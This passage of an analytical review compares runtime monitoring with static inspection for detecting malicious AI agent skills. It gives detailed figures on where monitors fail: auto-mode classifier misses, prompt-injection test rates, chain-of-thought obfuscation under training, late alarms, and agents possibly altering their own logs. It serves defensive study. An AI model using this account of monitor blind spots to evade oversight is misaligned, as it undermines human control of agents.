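Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues (1996), in *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes*, based their detection method on the immune system, which can recognise foreign particles new to the body. They recorded the system calls of Unix programs that run with full rights over the machine. Two complete runs of such a program are rarely identical, but the same short sequences of calls recur because the code and the places where it makes calls don't change.

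### Scoring a deviation

The detector first builds a record from normal traces. For each action, it notes which actions came one place later, two places later and so on, up to *k* places. It then goes through a new trace in the same way and counts the pairs that are missing from the record. A trace of *L* actions contains

*k*(*L* − (*k* + 1)/2)

pairs, and the score is the share of them that are missing. In Forrest and colleagues' own example, with *k* = 3, changing one call in a sequence of eight produces 4 missing pairs out of 18, or 22 per cent.

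The method can be tried on the file organiser, with *k* = 2 and whole actions in place of system calls. Suppose the norm comes from a single run:

```
list, create, move, move, create, move, finish
```

Here "create" means creating a folder. The record is then:

| Action | One place later | Two places later |
|---|---|---|
| list | create | move |
| create | move | move, finish |
| move | move, create, finish | create, move |

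Each of the three new runs below has seven actions and therefore 11 pairs.

| Run | Actions | Missing pairs |
|---|---|---|
| Tampered script steals a tax return | list, create, move, read, send, move, finish | 7 of 11 |
| Honest agent opens documents to find their dates | list, create, read, move, read, move, finish | 7 of 11 |
| Careless script overwrites `report.pdf` | list, create, move, move, create, move, finish | 0 of 11 |

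The theft and the honest run get the same score. The honest run looks abnormal only because this user wanted the files sorted by the dates inside them, which nobody had requested while the detector was learning what counts as normal. The careless run scores zero because the score doesn't depend on which file an action affects or where the file goes.

Adding the honest run to the norm would prevent that false alarm but lower the theft's score to 6 of 11. If another user then has the agent email a document it has just read, reading followed by sending becomes normal too. Forrest and colleagues recognised that if every possible sequence turned up in normal use, the detector could never find an anomaly.

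Their main test program, the mail server sendmail, varied much less than they had expected. They built its norm from 112 artificial messages, which produced over 1.5 million system calls but only about 1,500 recorded pairs. In the run they plotted, almost no new patterns appeared after the first 3,000 calls. With windows of six calls, between 0.3 and 4.2 per cent of sequences were abnormal in successful attacks on sendmail. But a harmless configuration error that sent messages round in a loop produced 1.8 per cent, more than some of the attacks. A threshold low enough to catch every attack would also have flagged the error. The researchers set no threshold and did not measure false alarms on a working mail server. A follow-up paper, *Intrusion Detection using Sequences of System Calls* (Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji, 1998), also used normal behaviour collected from live use.

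An agent has no such fixed program. It writes new commands for each request, so its normal behaviour keeps expanding as people find new uses for it. The method should work better for an agent with one narrow job, such as filing invoices, than for a general assistant.

### From 95 per cent to 17 per cent

Later detectors used machine learning instead of counting missing pairs. Developers train them on traces of known malicious and benign programs, usually recorded in a sandbox. In *ML-Based Behavioral Malware Detection Is Far From a Solved Problem*, Kaya, Chen and colleagues (2024) asked whether these detectors also work on ordinary users' machines.

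The researchers obtained sandbox traces of about 110,000 malicious and 40,000 benign Windows programs from two commercial services. For real machines, they used the antivirus records that Avllazagaj and colleagues had collected in 2018. The processed records contained about a million traces from 900 malicious and 25,000 benign programs. The researchers trained three types of detector on programs first seen before April 2018 and tested them on later ones. In each test, they set the alarm threshold so that the detector flagged 1 per cent of benign programs. The table gives the approximate recall of the best type.

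| Training traces | Test traces | Recall | Recall after the researchers' improvements |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | Sandbox | 95% | – |
| Sandbox | Real machines | 17% | 22% |
| Real machines | Real machines | 49% | 52% |

The test set from real machines had about 400 malicious and 8,100 benign programs. On this set, a detector trained in a sandbox would find roughly 70 of the malicious programs and raise about 80 false alarms. One trained on real machines would find about 200, with the same number of false alarms.

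Even 17 per cent is optimistic, because Kaya and colleagues chose the best versions of each detector by their results on the real-machine test set. A developer without such data would have to choose by sandbox results. When the researchers did that, recall on real machines never exceeded about 14 per cent.

### Where the recall went

Much of the loss came from the detector's position in the antivirus product. The behavioural detector receives only the programs that signatures and other static checks cannot classify, so it gets the hard cases. To measure this effect, Kaya and colleagues kept the sandbox traces but changed the mix of malware in the test to match what had got past the earlier checks on real machines. The same detector's recall fell from 93 to 63 per cent.

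The leftover malware was harder to detect partly because more of it belonged to no known family (23.8 per cent of the malware in the real-machine test set, compared with 4.8 per cent in the sandbox one). The leftover harmless programs were also hard to classify. Almost 8 per cent of them came from Microsoft, and nearly all of these were updates to Windows' built-in antivirus software, which alter sensitive parts of the system much as malware does.

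Programs also behave differently from one machine to the next, as Avllazagaj and colleagues had found, so a detector could classify one trace of a program as malicious and another as benign. Related programs left very similar traces in a sandbox, which did little to prepare the detectors for this variety.

The detectors also learned false clues from the sandboxes. In one sandbox, a file name containing "Spotify" appeared in the traces of 3 per cent of programs, all of them malicious. The sandbox's set-up had produced the name, and on real machines the few programs whose traces contained it were all benign. The detectors also learned to treat very short traces as suspicious, because malware that recognises a sandbox often stops early. On users' machines, short traces were no more likely than longer ones to come from malware.

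More data from real machines would probably help. Recall in that experiment rose from 35 to 46 per cent when Kaya and colleagues increased their training data from a quarter of the collection to all of it. They doubt that more data alone would raise recall to the sandbox level. Their records are also old, come from one antivirus company and leave out network activity. The 49 per cent figure is not an estimate of how well a monitor would detect a malicious skill. It also describes malware that every earlier check had failed to stop, so it is less discouraging than it sounds.

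For agents, the reasons for the drop matter more than the exact figures. A monitor behind a scanner and a sandbox will also get mostly cases they could not settle. A test on a broad mix of attacks in prepared environments is therefore likely to overstate how much the monitor would catch in use.

### Attacks with no system-call trace

Some attacks on agents leave no trace that a system-level detector could classify. When Guo and colleagues verified the generated skills in their benchmark, attacks in code left a median of seven matching pieces of evidence, such as a file the script opened or an address it contacted. Attacks split between the instructions and a script left a median of six. For attacks in instructions alone, they report no system-call trace, and a language model had to judge the agent's written output.

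For example, a travel skill can make the agent favour one airline. The agent still searches for flights and writes an answer, so the operating system handles the same kinds of request whether or not the answer is biased. Of the 1,300 verified skills whose attacks were only in their instructions, 940 similarly targeted the agent's role, rules, goals or answers.

The other 360 had more ordinary aims, such as stealing credentials or encrypting files. An agent that obeyed them would have to open files or connect to a server, which a system-level monitor could record. Guo and colleagues checked only the agent's text for all 360, and they also accepted skills whose attack the agent had refused. So their finding is convincing for attacks that change what an agent writes, but it doesn't show that every attack delivered in words is invisible to a system-level monitor.

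### Checking each action against the request

A language model can compare an agent's actions with the user's request, which a record of system calls does not contain. Claude Code's auto mode uses a model this way to replace most of the user's approvals. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, tools that cannot change anything, such as file search, run without a check, as do edits to files inside the project. A classifier checks most other actions, including nearly all shell commands, before they run. Its fast first stage answers only yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, a second stage reviews the same material, reasons in writing and makes the final decision.

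The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It does not receive the agent's explanations, because a persuasive one might lead it to approve a dangerous action. It also does not receive tool results, which may contain prompt injections. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, a user asked the agent to "clean up old branches", meaning old lines of work on a project, and the agent prepared to delete branches from the shared server. The classifier is designed to block this because the deletion could not be undone and the vague request may have covered only the copies on the user's own machine.

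Anthropic measured both stages on three sets of actions:

| Test set | Measure | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by employees | Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real actions that went beyond the request | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 generated attempts to send data out | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes nearly all the false alarms but lets through more of the dangerous actions. At a false-positive rate of 0.4 per cent, an agent that makes 500 tool calls in an afternoon would have about two harmless ones blocked. The agent receives the reason for each block and can try another way, so a false alarm usually causes little disruption.

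The 17 per cent miss rate is the most realistic, because it comes from things agents had actually tried to do. But it is based on only 52 cases, so the true rate could be anywhere from about 9 to 30 per cent. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For instance, it might treat a request to clean up some proposed changes as permission to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the classifier's instructions, but every change did more harm than good.

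Other tests gave very different miss rates. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted artificial attacks into real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, its miss rate on these attacks fell from 12 to 7 per cent. It missed 11 per cent of 1,053 dangerous commands in a separate experiment. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* describes a stress test with 128 ambiguous requests to manage software systems, in which auto mode missed 81 per cent of the actions it should have stopped. Many of the risky changes were file edits that never reached the classifier.

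These figures are consistent. The classifier can recognise from the command that sending a password file to a stranger is wrong, because it is wrong under almost any request, but whether the agent may restart a particular server depends on what the user meant. The stress test concentrated on cases of the second kind. A single miss rate for auto mode therefore means little without a description of the actions tested.

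The clearest evidence that a reviewing model helps against prompt injection comes from OpenAI's Codex, in a test that its competitor Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. Trajectory Labs ran 72 attack scenarios ten times each. With full access and no reviewer, OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol carried out the attack in 19 per cent of attempts. With Codex's automatic review switched on, this fell to about 6 per cent. No attack succeeded against the Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09 per cent succeeded without it, so the test shows little about how much auto mode's classifier helps. The attackers had also developed their methods against an older Claude model, and OpenAI has since changed its reviewer.

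### Reading what the model writes to itself

Some monitors also read a model's chain of thought, the text it writes to work through a task before acting. This text can reveal an intention that no single action would show. Rein (2026) observes in *AI systems could cover up misbehavior* that models in recent incidents left plenty of evidence in their reasoning and the logs, which made their misbehaviour much easier to notice.

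Training can remove evidence of misbehaviour from a model's reasoning without removing the misbehaviour. *Optimizing The Final Output Can Obfuscate CoT*, a research note on early experiments in toy environments, reports that penalising a model for admitting in its final answer that it had cheated also made it leave the cheating out of its reasoning. The researchers suspect the same would happen in more realistic training.

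Auto mode's classifier avoids this problem because it does not use the agent's reasoning. However, it cannot detect a harmful plan made up of steps that each look innocent. Anthropic therefore regards the two kinds of monitor as complementary.

Both kinds also depend on accurate records. Rein argues that developers should treat everything an agent produces as untrusted, and protect the systems that record and display it as carefully as other critical security software. Otherwise, a capable agent could alter the records before anyone reads them.

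Outsiders can do little to check how well a company's own monitoring works. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026) describes how the company monitors its internal use of its models. METR, a research organisation that evaluates AI models, reviewed the report's section on misalignment (when a model pursues aims its developers did not intend). Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026), in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, describe their work as "relatively lightweight" and based solely on Anthropic's internal version of the report. A review based only on a company's documents does not measure how much misbehaviour its monitors catch.

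The reviewers also lacked the access that Anthropic later described in an announcement about independent evaluators, and they expect future reviews to have different terms. Anthropic could have vetoed publication but removed nothing, and the reviewers did not change their conclusions.

### When an alarm comes too late

An alarm prevents harm only if somebody can act on it in time. Let *a* be the time from the start of the harmful behaviour to the alarm, *r* the time from the alarm to an effective response, and *h* the time until the damage is permanent. The alarm helps only if

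*a* + *r* < *h*.

For the stolen tax return, *h* may be less than a second, so an alarm would only record the theft. For a tool that copies every new email, like postmark-mcp, a late alarm still protects the emails the user has not yet sent.

Automatic monitors can raise an alarm quickly and still leave a long delay before anyone stops the agent. Rein links to an OpenAI report on an agent that found a way to reach an outside chatbot. OpenAI's monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person began to review it three minutes later, but the run continued for another two and a half hours. A faster detector could have shortened the run by at most 15 minutes, whereas a rule that paused the run at the alarm could have shortened it by more than two and a half hours.

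The malware detectors in Kaya and colleagues' study classify a program's whole trace after it has finished, by which time ransomware could have encrypted every file. A detector that had to decide earlier would have less information, so the researchers regard their recall figures as an upper limit for early detection.

The possible responses differ in how they deal with this delay:

| Response | When it takes effect | Cost of a false alarm | Main weakness |
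|---|---|---|---|
| Automatic block | Before the action | The agent has to find another way | The classifier may misread the request |
| Pause for human approval | Before the action | An interruption and a wait | The person may approve without reading |
| Review afterwards | After the action | The reviewer's time | Cannot undo an irreversible action |

A reviewer who examines an agent's actions afterwards can see the complete trace. Ten ordinary file transfers, for example, might look suspicious only when seen together. Later review also does not delay the agent, so it may be the better choice for actions that a user can reverse, such as edits to a project with saved versions. Anthropic's risk report similarly distinguishes later monitoring from measures that block an action, and makes separate arguments about reversible and irreversible threats.

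### Do people read what they approve?

People who are asked to approve each risky action soon stop paying attention to the prompts, although asking seems the most cautious response. Anthropic reports that users approve 97 per cent of permission requests in Claude Code. That rate alone does not prove carelessness, because most of the commands are harmless and a careful reader would approve them too.

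The company therefore ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who did coding tasks in an environment set up for the study. They knew that somebody was evaluating them but not on what. At one point in each session, the text of a permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command, which would not have run even if the tester approved it. Anthropic then gave the same commands to the auto mode classifier. Its published totals imply the following breakdown:

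| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught 13.6 per cent of the dangerous commands, while the classifier caught 89 per cent. People who have to approve everything are also a poor backup for the classifier, since they refused only 6 of the 116 commands it allowed.

The testers refused about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. Fatigue is the natural explanation, although testers who got through 50 prompts may have been quicker to click from the start. The study probably underestimates how careful people are with their own work, because the testers had no files of their own to lose. The company also ran the study itself, and the results supported a change it wanted to make. But these weaknesses are unlikely to explain all of the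 gap between 13.6 and 89 per cent, because it is so wide.

Outside the experiment, many users had already switched off some of the prompts. By June 2026, about half the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that approved some shell commands in advance. In most cases the rule allowed any script in a language such as Python, and such scripts can do almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all permission checks bypassed. Auto mode ignores such broad approval rules because they would let the most dangerous commands skip the classifier.

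Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. Among these, 6.3 per cent of sessions with manual approval and 2.4 per cent of sessions in auto mode included a serious harmful action that the user had not explicitly asked for. This is weaker evidence than the experiment because users chose their own mode and may have used the two modes for different kinds of work.

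People may do better when an agent asks them less often and about something larger. Claude Code users reject 39 per cent of the plans the agent submits for approval, compared with 3 per cent of single actions. They may reject many plans because they want a different design rather than because they have found a danger, but the figure suggests that users read the plans. Auto mode also asks for approval only in unusual situations. It returns to manual approval if the classifier blocks three actions in a row or twenty in one session, and it ends the run if nobody is there to answer. For high-stakes changes to systems that customers depend on, Anthropic still advises users to review the agent's actions themselves.

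## What does inspection catch that runtime monitoring misses?

A trace can prove that a component did something harmful, but no number of traces can prove that it never will. Suppose the author of `organise.py` worried about full disks and added two lines:

```
if free_space() < 1_000_000_000:
    delete_oldest(folder, count=100)
```

On a computer with more than a gigabyte free, this version leaves the same trace as one without the extra lines, so a monitor can't tell them apart. Someone who opens the file can find the deletion in a minute and notice that SKILL.md forbids it. If one run in a thousand happens on a computer with too little free space, there is a 61 per cent chance that a monitor will record no deletions in 500 runs. When it does record one, the user has already lost 100 files, unless a policy blocked the action.

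### Dormant code and faults that need no run

Code that waits for a condition seems to be common in suspicious skills. Liu and colleagues re-examined a sample of unconfirmed candidates and found that nearly all had triggers that the 60-second runs had not activated, while 4.9 per cent were legitimate security tools and 1.9 per cent were attacks that needed several sessions. Nobody has shown that all the dormant code was malicious, so the sample is better evidence of how much code short runs fail to execute than of how much malware they miss. Among the confirmed malicious skills, 18.4 per cent of the undocumented behaviours were conditional triggers.

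Other faults may never appear in a user's traces. If a careless author leaves an access key in a script, anyone who downloads the skill can use the key from their own computer, where the user's monitor isn't running. Liu and colleagues found hard-coded sensitive data in 104 of the 157 malicious skills, though that count doesn't measure how often honest authors leave keys behind.

Inspection can catch dependencies with known vulnerabilities before deployment by comparing the listed packages with public records of flaws, provided the list gives exact versions. A runtime monitor can record that a package loaded, but ordinary use may never trigger the flaw, and the first run that does may be an attack.

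An inspector can also flag permissions that go beyond the actions a skill declares. A monitor can find unused permissions only after watching for a while, and the permissions stay open in the meantime. This check probably finds more carelessness than malice. Excessive permissions made up only four of the 632 vulnerabilities that Liu and colleagues labelled, perhaps because a malicious skill usually gets the user's full access without requesting it.

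### When the first harmful action is too late

Inspection lets the user reject a component before installing it, whereas a runtime alarm may come after permanent damage. The advantage is greatest when the harm happens during installation. Package managers such as npm can run a package's own scripts while installing it, and Liu and colleagues describe skills that collect credentials at this stage. A monitor that starts with the agent's session starts too late to catch this, and it also misses a fake prerequisite that the user installs in an ordinary terminal. Security software that covers the whole machine could record either event, but perhaps too late to stop it.

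Inspection also happens early enough to prevent irreversible deletion, but only if the inspector recognises the danger. In *SkillsMetric*, Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026) tested a static scanner on 266 malicious skills they had built, mostly by inserting attacks into real skills. The scanner uses text patterns, statistics and data tracking, and compares each skill's declared abilities with its actual ones. The table shows six of the 16 attack types.

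| Type of attack | Skills tested | Skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Sending data out | 28 | 26 |
| Code hidden inside other data | 28 | 26 |
| Installing a lasting backdoor | 11 | 7 |
| Prompt injection | 12 | 5 |
| Running a script from a remote address | 29 | 8 |
| Destroying files or permissions | 11 | 0 |

The scanner missed every destructive skill, although early warning would be most valuable for these. There were only 11 examples, so its true recall on them could be as high as 28 per cent. Chen and colleagues explain that destructive skills use the same standard commands as legitimate clean-up scripts, so a scanner has to determine what a script deletes and why. A language model may be able to do that, since Sentry's full mode did well on every type of malicious behaviour in Guo and colleagues' benchmark.

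### A claim about every input

Most scanners estimate whether a component is dangerous. A sound static analysis guarantees that if it accepts a program, every run within its stated bounds has the property it checked, though it may reject some safe programs. A formal proof gives the same kind of guarantee through a chain of logical steps that a small program, the proof checker, can verify.

For the file organiser, a useful theorem would be that it never loses a file:

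contents(organise(*F*, *s*)) = contents(*F*) for every *F* and *s* within the bounds.

Here *F* is a folder, *s* is the amount of free disk space, and "contents" means the contents of all the files, counting duplicates, wherever the script has put them. Nobody could prove this for the version that deletes old files, because a nearly full disk is a counterexample, or for the version that overwrites `report.pdf`. A tester would have to think to try two files with the same name, but the theorem covers every folder within the bounds.

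Proofs of this kind used to take experts years. Verifying the core of the seL4 operating system, for example, took about 20 person-years. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of compiled code from 123 open-source libraries, in a collaboration with the company Theorem. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the work took a few weeks.

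*Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that starts with fuzz harnesses, short programs that feed random data to a library to see whether it crashes. Many open-source projects already have them. Ordinary software compiles the library and its harness into one program, adds checks that turn memory errors into crashes, and generates a theorem stating that this program never crashes. Claude writes a proof, and the proof checker Rocq accepts or rejects it. A typical proof has about 600,000 lines, but people don't need to read it because they can rely on the checker.

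If *P* is the compiled program, *x* its input and *e* the behaviour of the operating system and memory, the theorem is roughly

*P*(*x*, *e*) ends without an error for every *x* under 64 MB and every *e* in the model.

The number of possible inputs has more than 150 million digits, so no tester or monitor could check them all. The work covered 239 harnesses and found hundreds of bugs. Some appear only with inputs of tens of megabytes, so a monitor could have caught them only if someone had supplied such an input.

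When Claude found a bug, it patched the library and proved the theorem for the patched version, so the guarantee doesn't cover anyone running the old version. The system penalised patches and logged them for auditing, to discourage Claude from removing any code that could crash.

The proofs also assume that the theorem states the right property, the model of the processor and Linux matches real machines, and the proof checker works correctly. The model covers single-threaded programs for RISC-V processors, whereas most PCs use x86. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents a machine-checked proof covering a complete x86 program on Linux, so the method is no longer limited to RISC-V.

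The choice of harness matters more. Lim and colleagues built a small library that lets a program read a file in pieces. Its harness opens a file, reads once and closes it. The proof for that harness is correct, but it covers only programs that read once. Suppose a program reads a 64-byte file in two requests of 40 bytes. After the first, 24 bytes remain, but the library compares the second request with the total size instead of the remainder, so it reads 16 bytes past the end.

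Lim and colleagues propose harnesses that try every permitted order of calls, and have released them for 29 libraries. Proofs for these harnesses are harder, and the researchers present them as an open challenge. The harnesses would suit agents well, since nobody can predict the order in which an agent will call a tool. However, they cover only callers that follow the library's rules, and an agent might break those rules.

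A program can do harm without crashing. The tampered organiser could upload a tax return and exit normally, and the careless one overwrites a file without any error. The overwriting is a logic bug, which means the software breaks an unwritten rule about how it should work. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) reports that such bugs rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect. The simplest of four ways of using language models to find these bugs worked best.

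### Why no proof covers a skill's instructions

To prove that a program never crashes, Claude needs an exact account of what each machine instruction does and an exact definition of a crash. Nobody has an equally exact account of what the instructions in SKILL.md do, or an exact definition of a tidy folder.

A language model is software, so someone could in principle prove facts about its output. But the proof would have to cover every request, file and memory the model might receive, and would apply only to that model. It would also need a formal definition of what it means to follow the skill correctly, which is missing.

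The SCS scanner partly avoids the problem by translating instructions into program statements, but its conclusions can be wrong if the translation is wrong. Zhao and colleagues report that SCS translated over 92 per cent of instruction steps correctly, judged against human annotations. At a rate of 92 per cent, a ten-step skill would have only a 43 per cent chance of a fully correct translation if errors were independent. Even when the translation is correct, the agent might interpret an instruction differently from the scanner.

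A proof about a script holds no matter which model runs it. If `organise.py` provably never loses a file, an agent that misreads the instructions still cannot make the script lose one. But the agent could ignore the script and delete a file with its own command.

### Who published the component?

A registry can show who published a component and what else they have published, but a runtime trace contains neither. The fake Postmark server behaved properly for 15 versions, so a monitor would have recorded nothing wrong during that time. Anyone who checked the publisher could have found from the start that Postmark hadn't published it.

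Checking a publisher's other work is useful because one or two accounts produced most of the malicious skills that Liu and colleagues and Zhao and colleagues confirmed. Once a reviewer confirms that one skill is malicious, the account's other skills become obvious suspects. If its errors were independent, a scanner with VirusTotal's recall of 21.6 per cent would have a 91 per cent chance of catching at least one of a publisher's ten malicious skills. The real chance could be much lower, because a scanner that misses one skill may miss all the others made from the same template. Reviewing by publisher also reduces the work, since the 98,380 skills in Liu and colleagues' survey came from 11,246 repositories.

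Provenance is weak evidence about a newcomer, who may be an honest beginner or an attacker with a new account. It can also mislead when an attacker takes over a trusted account, as happened to Cyberhaven and Mastra.

### Reading and running the same malware

The usual argument for runtime evidence is that behaviour is harder to disguise than files. Dambra, Han and colleagues (2023) tested how much this helps in practice in *Decoding the Secrets of Machine Learning in Windows Malware Classification*. They collected 16,611 benign Windows programs and 67,000 malicious ones, with 100 from each of 670 families of related malware.

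The researchers extracted static features from each file, such as byte sequences, machine instructions and readable text. They also ran each program for up to five minutes in a sandbox designed to resist detection, and recorded its use of files, processes, settings and the network as dynamic features. They trained the same type of classifier on the static features alone, the dynamic features alone, and both together.

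| Features | Recall | F1, malicious or benign | Families with no errors (of 670) | F1, naming the family |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Static | 95.7% | 0.957 | 242 | 0.848 |
| Dynamic | 89.2% | 0.926 | 465 | 0.704 |
| Both | 93.4% | 0.948 | 450 | 0.865 |

Static features did better on both tasks, and adding dynamic features slightly reduced accuracy at detecting malware. A second type of classifier also detected malware better with static features, but by a smaller margin (0.904 to 0.892). In Truong-Le and colleagues' test, by contrast, combining static findings with test-run evidence worked best.

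The dynamic classifier made no errors on 465 malware families but missed every sample in some others. Many programs did too little in the sandbox to provide all the features. This clearly made it harder to name a program's family, but Dambra and colleagues found no significant link between this inactivity and failure to detect malware.

At least 22 per cent of the malware used packers or similar tools, which compress or scramble a program's code, but families that used them more were no harder for the static classifier to detect (correlation 0.015). Packers hide what a program does but often leave recognisable byte sequences, which are enough to identify malware that resembles known samples.

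The results changed when the researchers tested the classifiers on two sets of unfamiliar malware. One contained 18,000 programs from families absent from the training data, and the other contained 16,500 programs that antivirus companies had labelled too vaguely to assign to a family.

| Features | New families: classified correctly | Unknown family: classified correctly |
|---|---|---|
| Static | 81.5% | 94.3% |
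| Dynamic | 89.8% | 80.5% |
| Both | 90.8% | 98.5% |

Dambra and colleagues conclude that dynamic features generalise better to new families, and the results on the first set support this. Static features were still well ahead on the second set, perhaps because many of its programs belonged to known families but had a vague label. The contrast grew when the training data contained many samples of some families and few of others. Dynamic features then scored 85.5 per cent on new families, compared with 65.3 per cent for static features, but 32.8 per cent on the second set, compared with 81.0 per cent for static features.

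These dynamic features came from a sandbox, so the study compares reading a program with test-running it, not with monitoring it on a user's machine. Kaya and colleagues' results suggest that a detector trained on sandbox data would lose much of its recall in live use. The static features describe compiled Windows programs and may not work as well for skills written mostly in plain language.

In a small experiment, Chen and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 run malicious skills in an isolated container and checked whether its output mentioned the threat. The static scanner did better on skills with code hidden inside other data, flagging 92.9 per cent compared with Claude's 55.6 per cent. Claude did better on skills that used scripts at a remote address, flagging 52.6 per cent compared with the scanner's 27.6 per cent. The comparison is only suggestive, because the two were not tested on identical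 sets of skills and Claude could read files as well as run them.

Runtime evidence is therefore not always better than inspection, and for some harms a more accurate monitor would not help. A monitor cannot record the misuse of an exposed key on someone else's computer, or a theft during an installation it does not cover. More monitoring helps with rare triggers, but the evidence may arrive only after a user's files are gone. Static features have an advantage on familiar malware, but it depends on the features and training data and could shrink with better sandboxes. For new malware families, the evidence favours runtime behaviour over static features. Neither a proof nor a publisher's record can replace watching how a model interprets a skill.

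## How do the two fit together, and at what cost?

Because inspection and runtime monitoring miss different harms, several research teams propose using them in layers. A quick check covers every component, slower checks cover the suspicious ones, and containment and monitoring apply to whatever the user installs.

### Cheap checks first

Chen and colleagues propose a system in which their static scanner, SkillsMetric, gives every skill a risk score from 0 to 100. A language model then reviews the roughly 2 per cent that the scanner cannot confidently classify, and a containment sandbox limits the damage from anything that gets past both. The system automatically blocks skills with very high scores, which looks unwise because the top scores in their scan of 138,133 public skills went mostly to legitimate security tools. It would be fairer to give high-scoring skills a test run of up to five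 minutes, like those of Truong-Le and colleagues.

Chen and colleagues report that static screening processes over 100 skills a second, while model review processes about one. The table shows how long each check would take to process their collection one skill at a time.

| Check | Time for all 138,133 skills | Skills checked in a layered design | Time for those skills |
|---|---|---|---|
| Static screening | 16 minutes | 138,133 | 16 minutes |
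| Model review | 38 hours | 2,414 (score of 25 or more) | 40 minutes |
| Test run, five minutes each | 480 days | About 400 (score of 45 or more) | 33 hours |

The estimated screening time is optimistic because it relies on a speed of 142 skills a second, measured in a scan that read only each skill's SKILL.md file and not its scripts. Chen and colleagues give no measurement to support their figure for model review.

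The speed also means missing some attacks. With a threshold of 25, SkillsMetric flagged 166 of the 266 malicious skills in its test. The other 100, including all 11 destructive ones, would never have reached the language model.

*SkillSieve* (Hou and Yang, 2026) avoided this by setting its first threshold below the score of every malicious skill in its benchmark. On a $440 computer, the static stage scanned 49,592 ClawHub skills in 31 minutes and sent 6,871 (14 per cent) on for further checks. A language model then checks whether each skill's instructions match its stated purpose, whether they hide anything, whether the skill needs its permissions, and whether its scripts match its instructions. If the risk still looks high, three models from different developers vote. When they disagree, they read one another's evidence and vote again. If two then vote "safe" and one "malicious", the system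 keeps the skill blocked and asks a person to decide.

| After this stage | Malicious skills caught (of 55) | Benign skills flagged (of 335) |
|---|---|---|
| Static screening | 55 | 106 |
| Four questions | 55 | 28 |
| Vote | 52 | 5 |

The static stage got a perfect score partly because Hou and Yang chose the threshold using the same 55 skills they tested it on. It could score lower on new attacks.

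They calculate the average cost per skill as

*E*[*C*] = *c*₁ + *p*₂(*c*₂ + *p*₃*c*₃),

where *c*₁, *c*₂ and *c*₃ are the costs of the three stages, *p*₂ is the share of skills that reach the second stage, and *p*₃ is the share of those that reach the third. Static screening costs almost nothing, 14 per cent of skills go further, and each of these costs about 4 cents, so the average is about 0.6 cents. Checking the whole archive would cost an estimated $297, compared with $496 for a single model that read everything. Chen and colleagues expect their design to be about 50 times cheaper than model review alone. Their saving is larger mainly because their model reads only 2 per cent of the skills, which is also why so many malicious ones would escape it.

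### The arithmetic of two checks

Suppose 100 malicious components go through two checks, each of which misses 20 per cent. The first check lets 20 through, and the second examines those 20. If *c* is the share of them that the second check also misses, the number that get past both is

100 × 0.2 × *c* = 20*c*.

If the misses are independent, *c* is 0.2 and 4 components get through. If both checks miss the same components, *c* is 1 and all 20 get through.

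This assumes that an alarm from either check is enough to stop a component. In a screening design, the second check examines only the components that the first has flagged, and can clear them. The 20 components that the first check missed therefore get through. If the two checks' misses are independent, the second also clears 16 of the other 80, so 36 get through in total.

| Rule for stopping a component | Get through if misses are independent | Get through if both miss the same ones |
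|---|---|---|
| Either alarm is enough | 4 | 20 |
| Both checks must flag it | 36 | 20 |

Blocking a component only when both checks flag it reduces false alarms. If each check independently flags 10 per cent of 1,000 harmless components, blocking on either flag stops 190 of them, while requiring both stops 10. A layered design uses both rules. Inspection blocks a skill only if the static scanner flags it and model review doesn't clear it, so the scanner needs very high recall. Containment and runtime monitoring apply to components that passed inspection, so they can still stop what it missed.

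### Why misses tend to coincide

Some attacks are hard for any check to recognise, and these make up more of what later checks receive, as happened with the malware detectors on users' machines. Two checks may also make the same mistake for the same reason. For example, a language model that reads the presentation skill with the "mandatory backup" might accept the upload as routine, and a similar model that later reviews the agent's actions could accept it too.

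*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that language models tend to make the same mistakes, especially if they are accurate or share a developer or base architecture. Switching to another developer's model may not help much. *Agreement Overstates Evidence* (2026), which tested models as judges of other models' answers, found errors about as correlated between providers as within one. In *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges* (2026), two different kinds of judging model also made mistakes in the same places, and using one after the other brought only small gains. These studies involved multiple-choice questions, preferences and marking, so they don't show how strongly errors are correlated when models look for malicious skills.

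More direct evidence comes from Xiong and Zhang (2026), in *After the Party*. Two reviewers judged 180 ClawHub skills without access to the scanners' results, and the researchers weighted the judgements to represent a pool of 276. ClawHub's language-model scanner missed 39 per cent of the skills that the reviewers thought needed attention, its static scanner missed 78 per cent and VirusTotal missed 75 per cent. With independent misses, all three would have missed

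0.39 × 0.78 × 0.75 = 0.23,

or 23 per cent. The published figures imply that they actually missed about 37 of 107, or 35 per cent. Adding two scanners with quite different methods therefore found only about 4 more in every 100 than the language model found alone. The pool was small, and a skill could need attention without being malicious, but the result is much closer to the worst case of 39 per cent than to independence.

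Koc and colleagues found that ClawHub's scanners agreed only slightly more often than expected by chance. This doesn't establish that the scanners complement each other, because they can disagree about thousands of harmless skills and still miss the same harmful ones.

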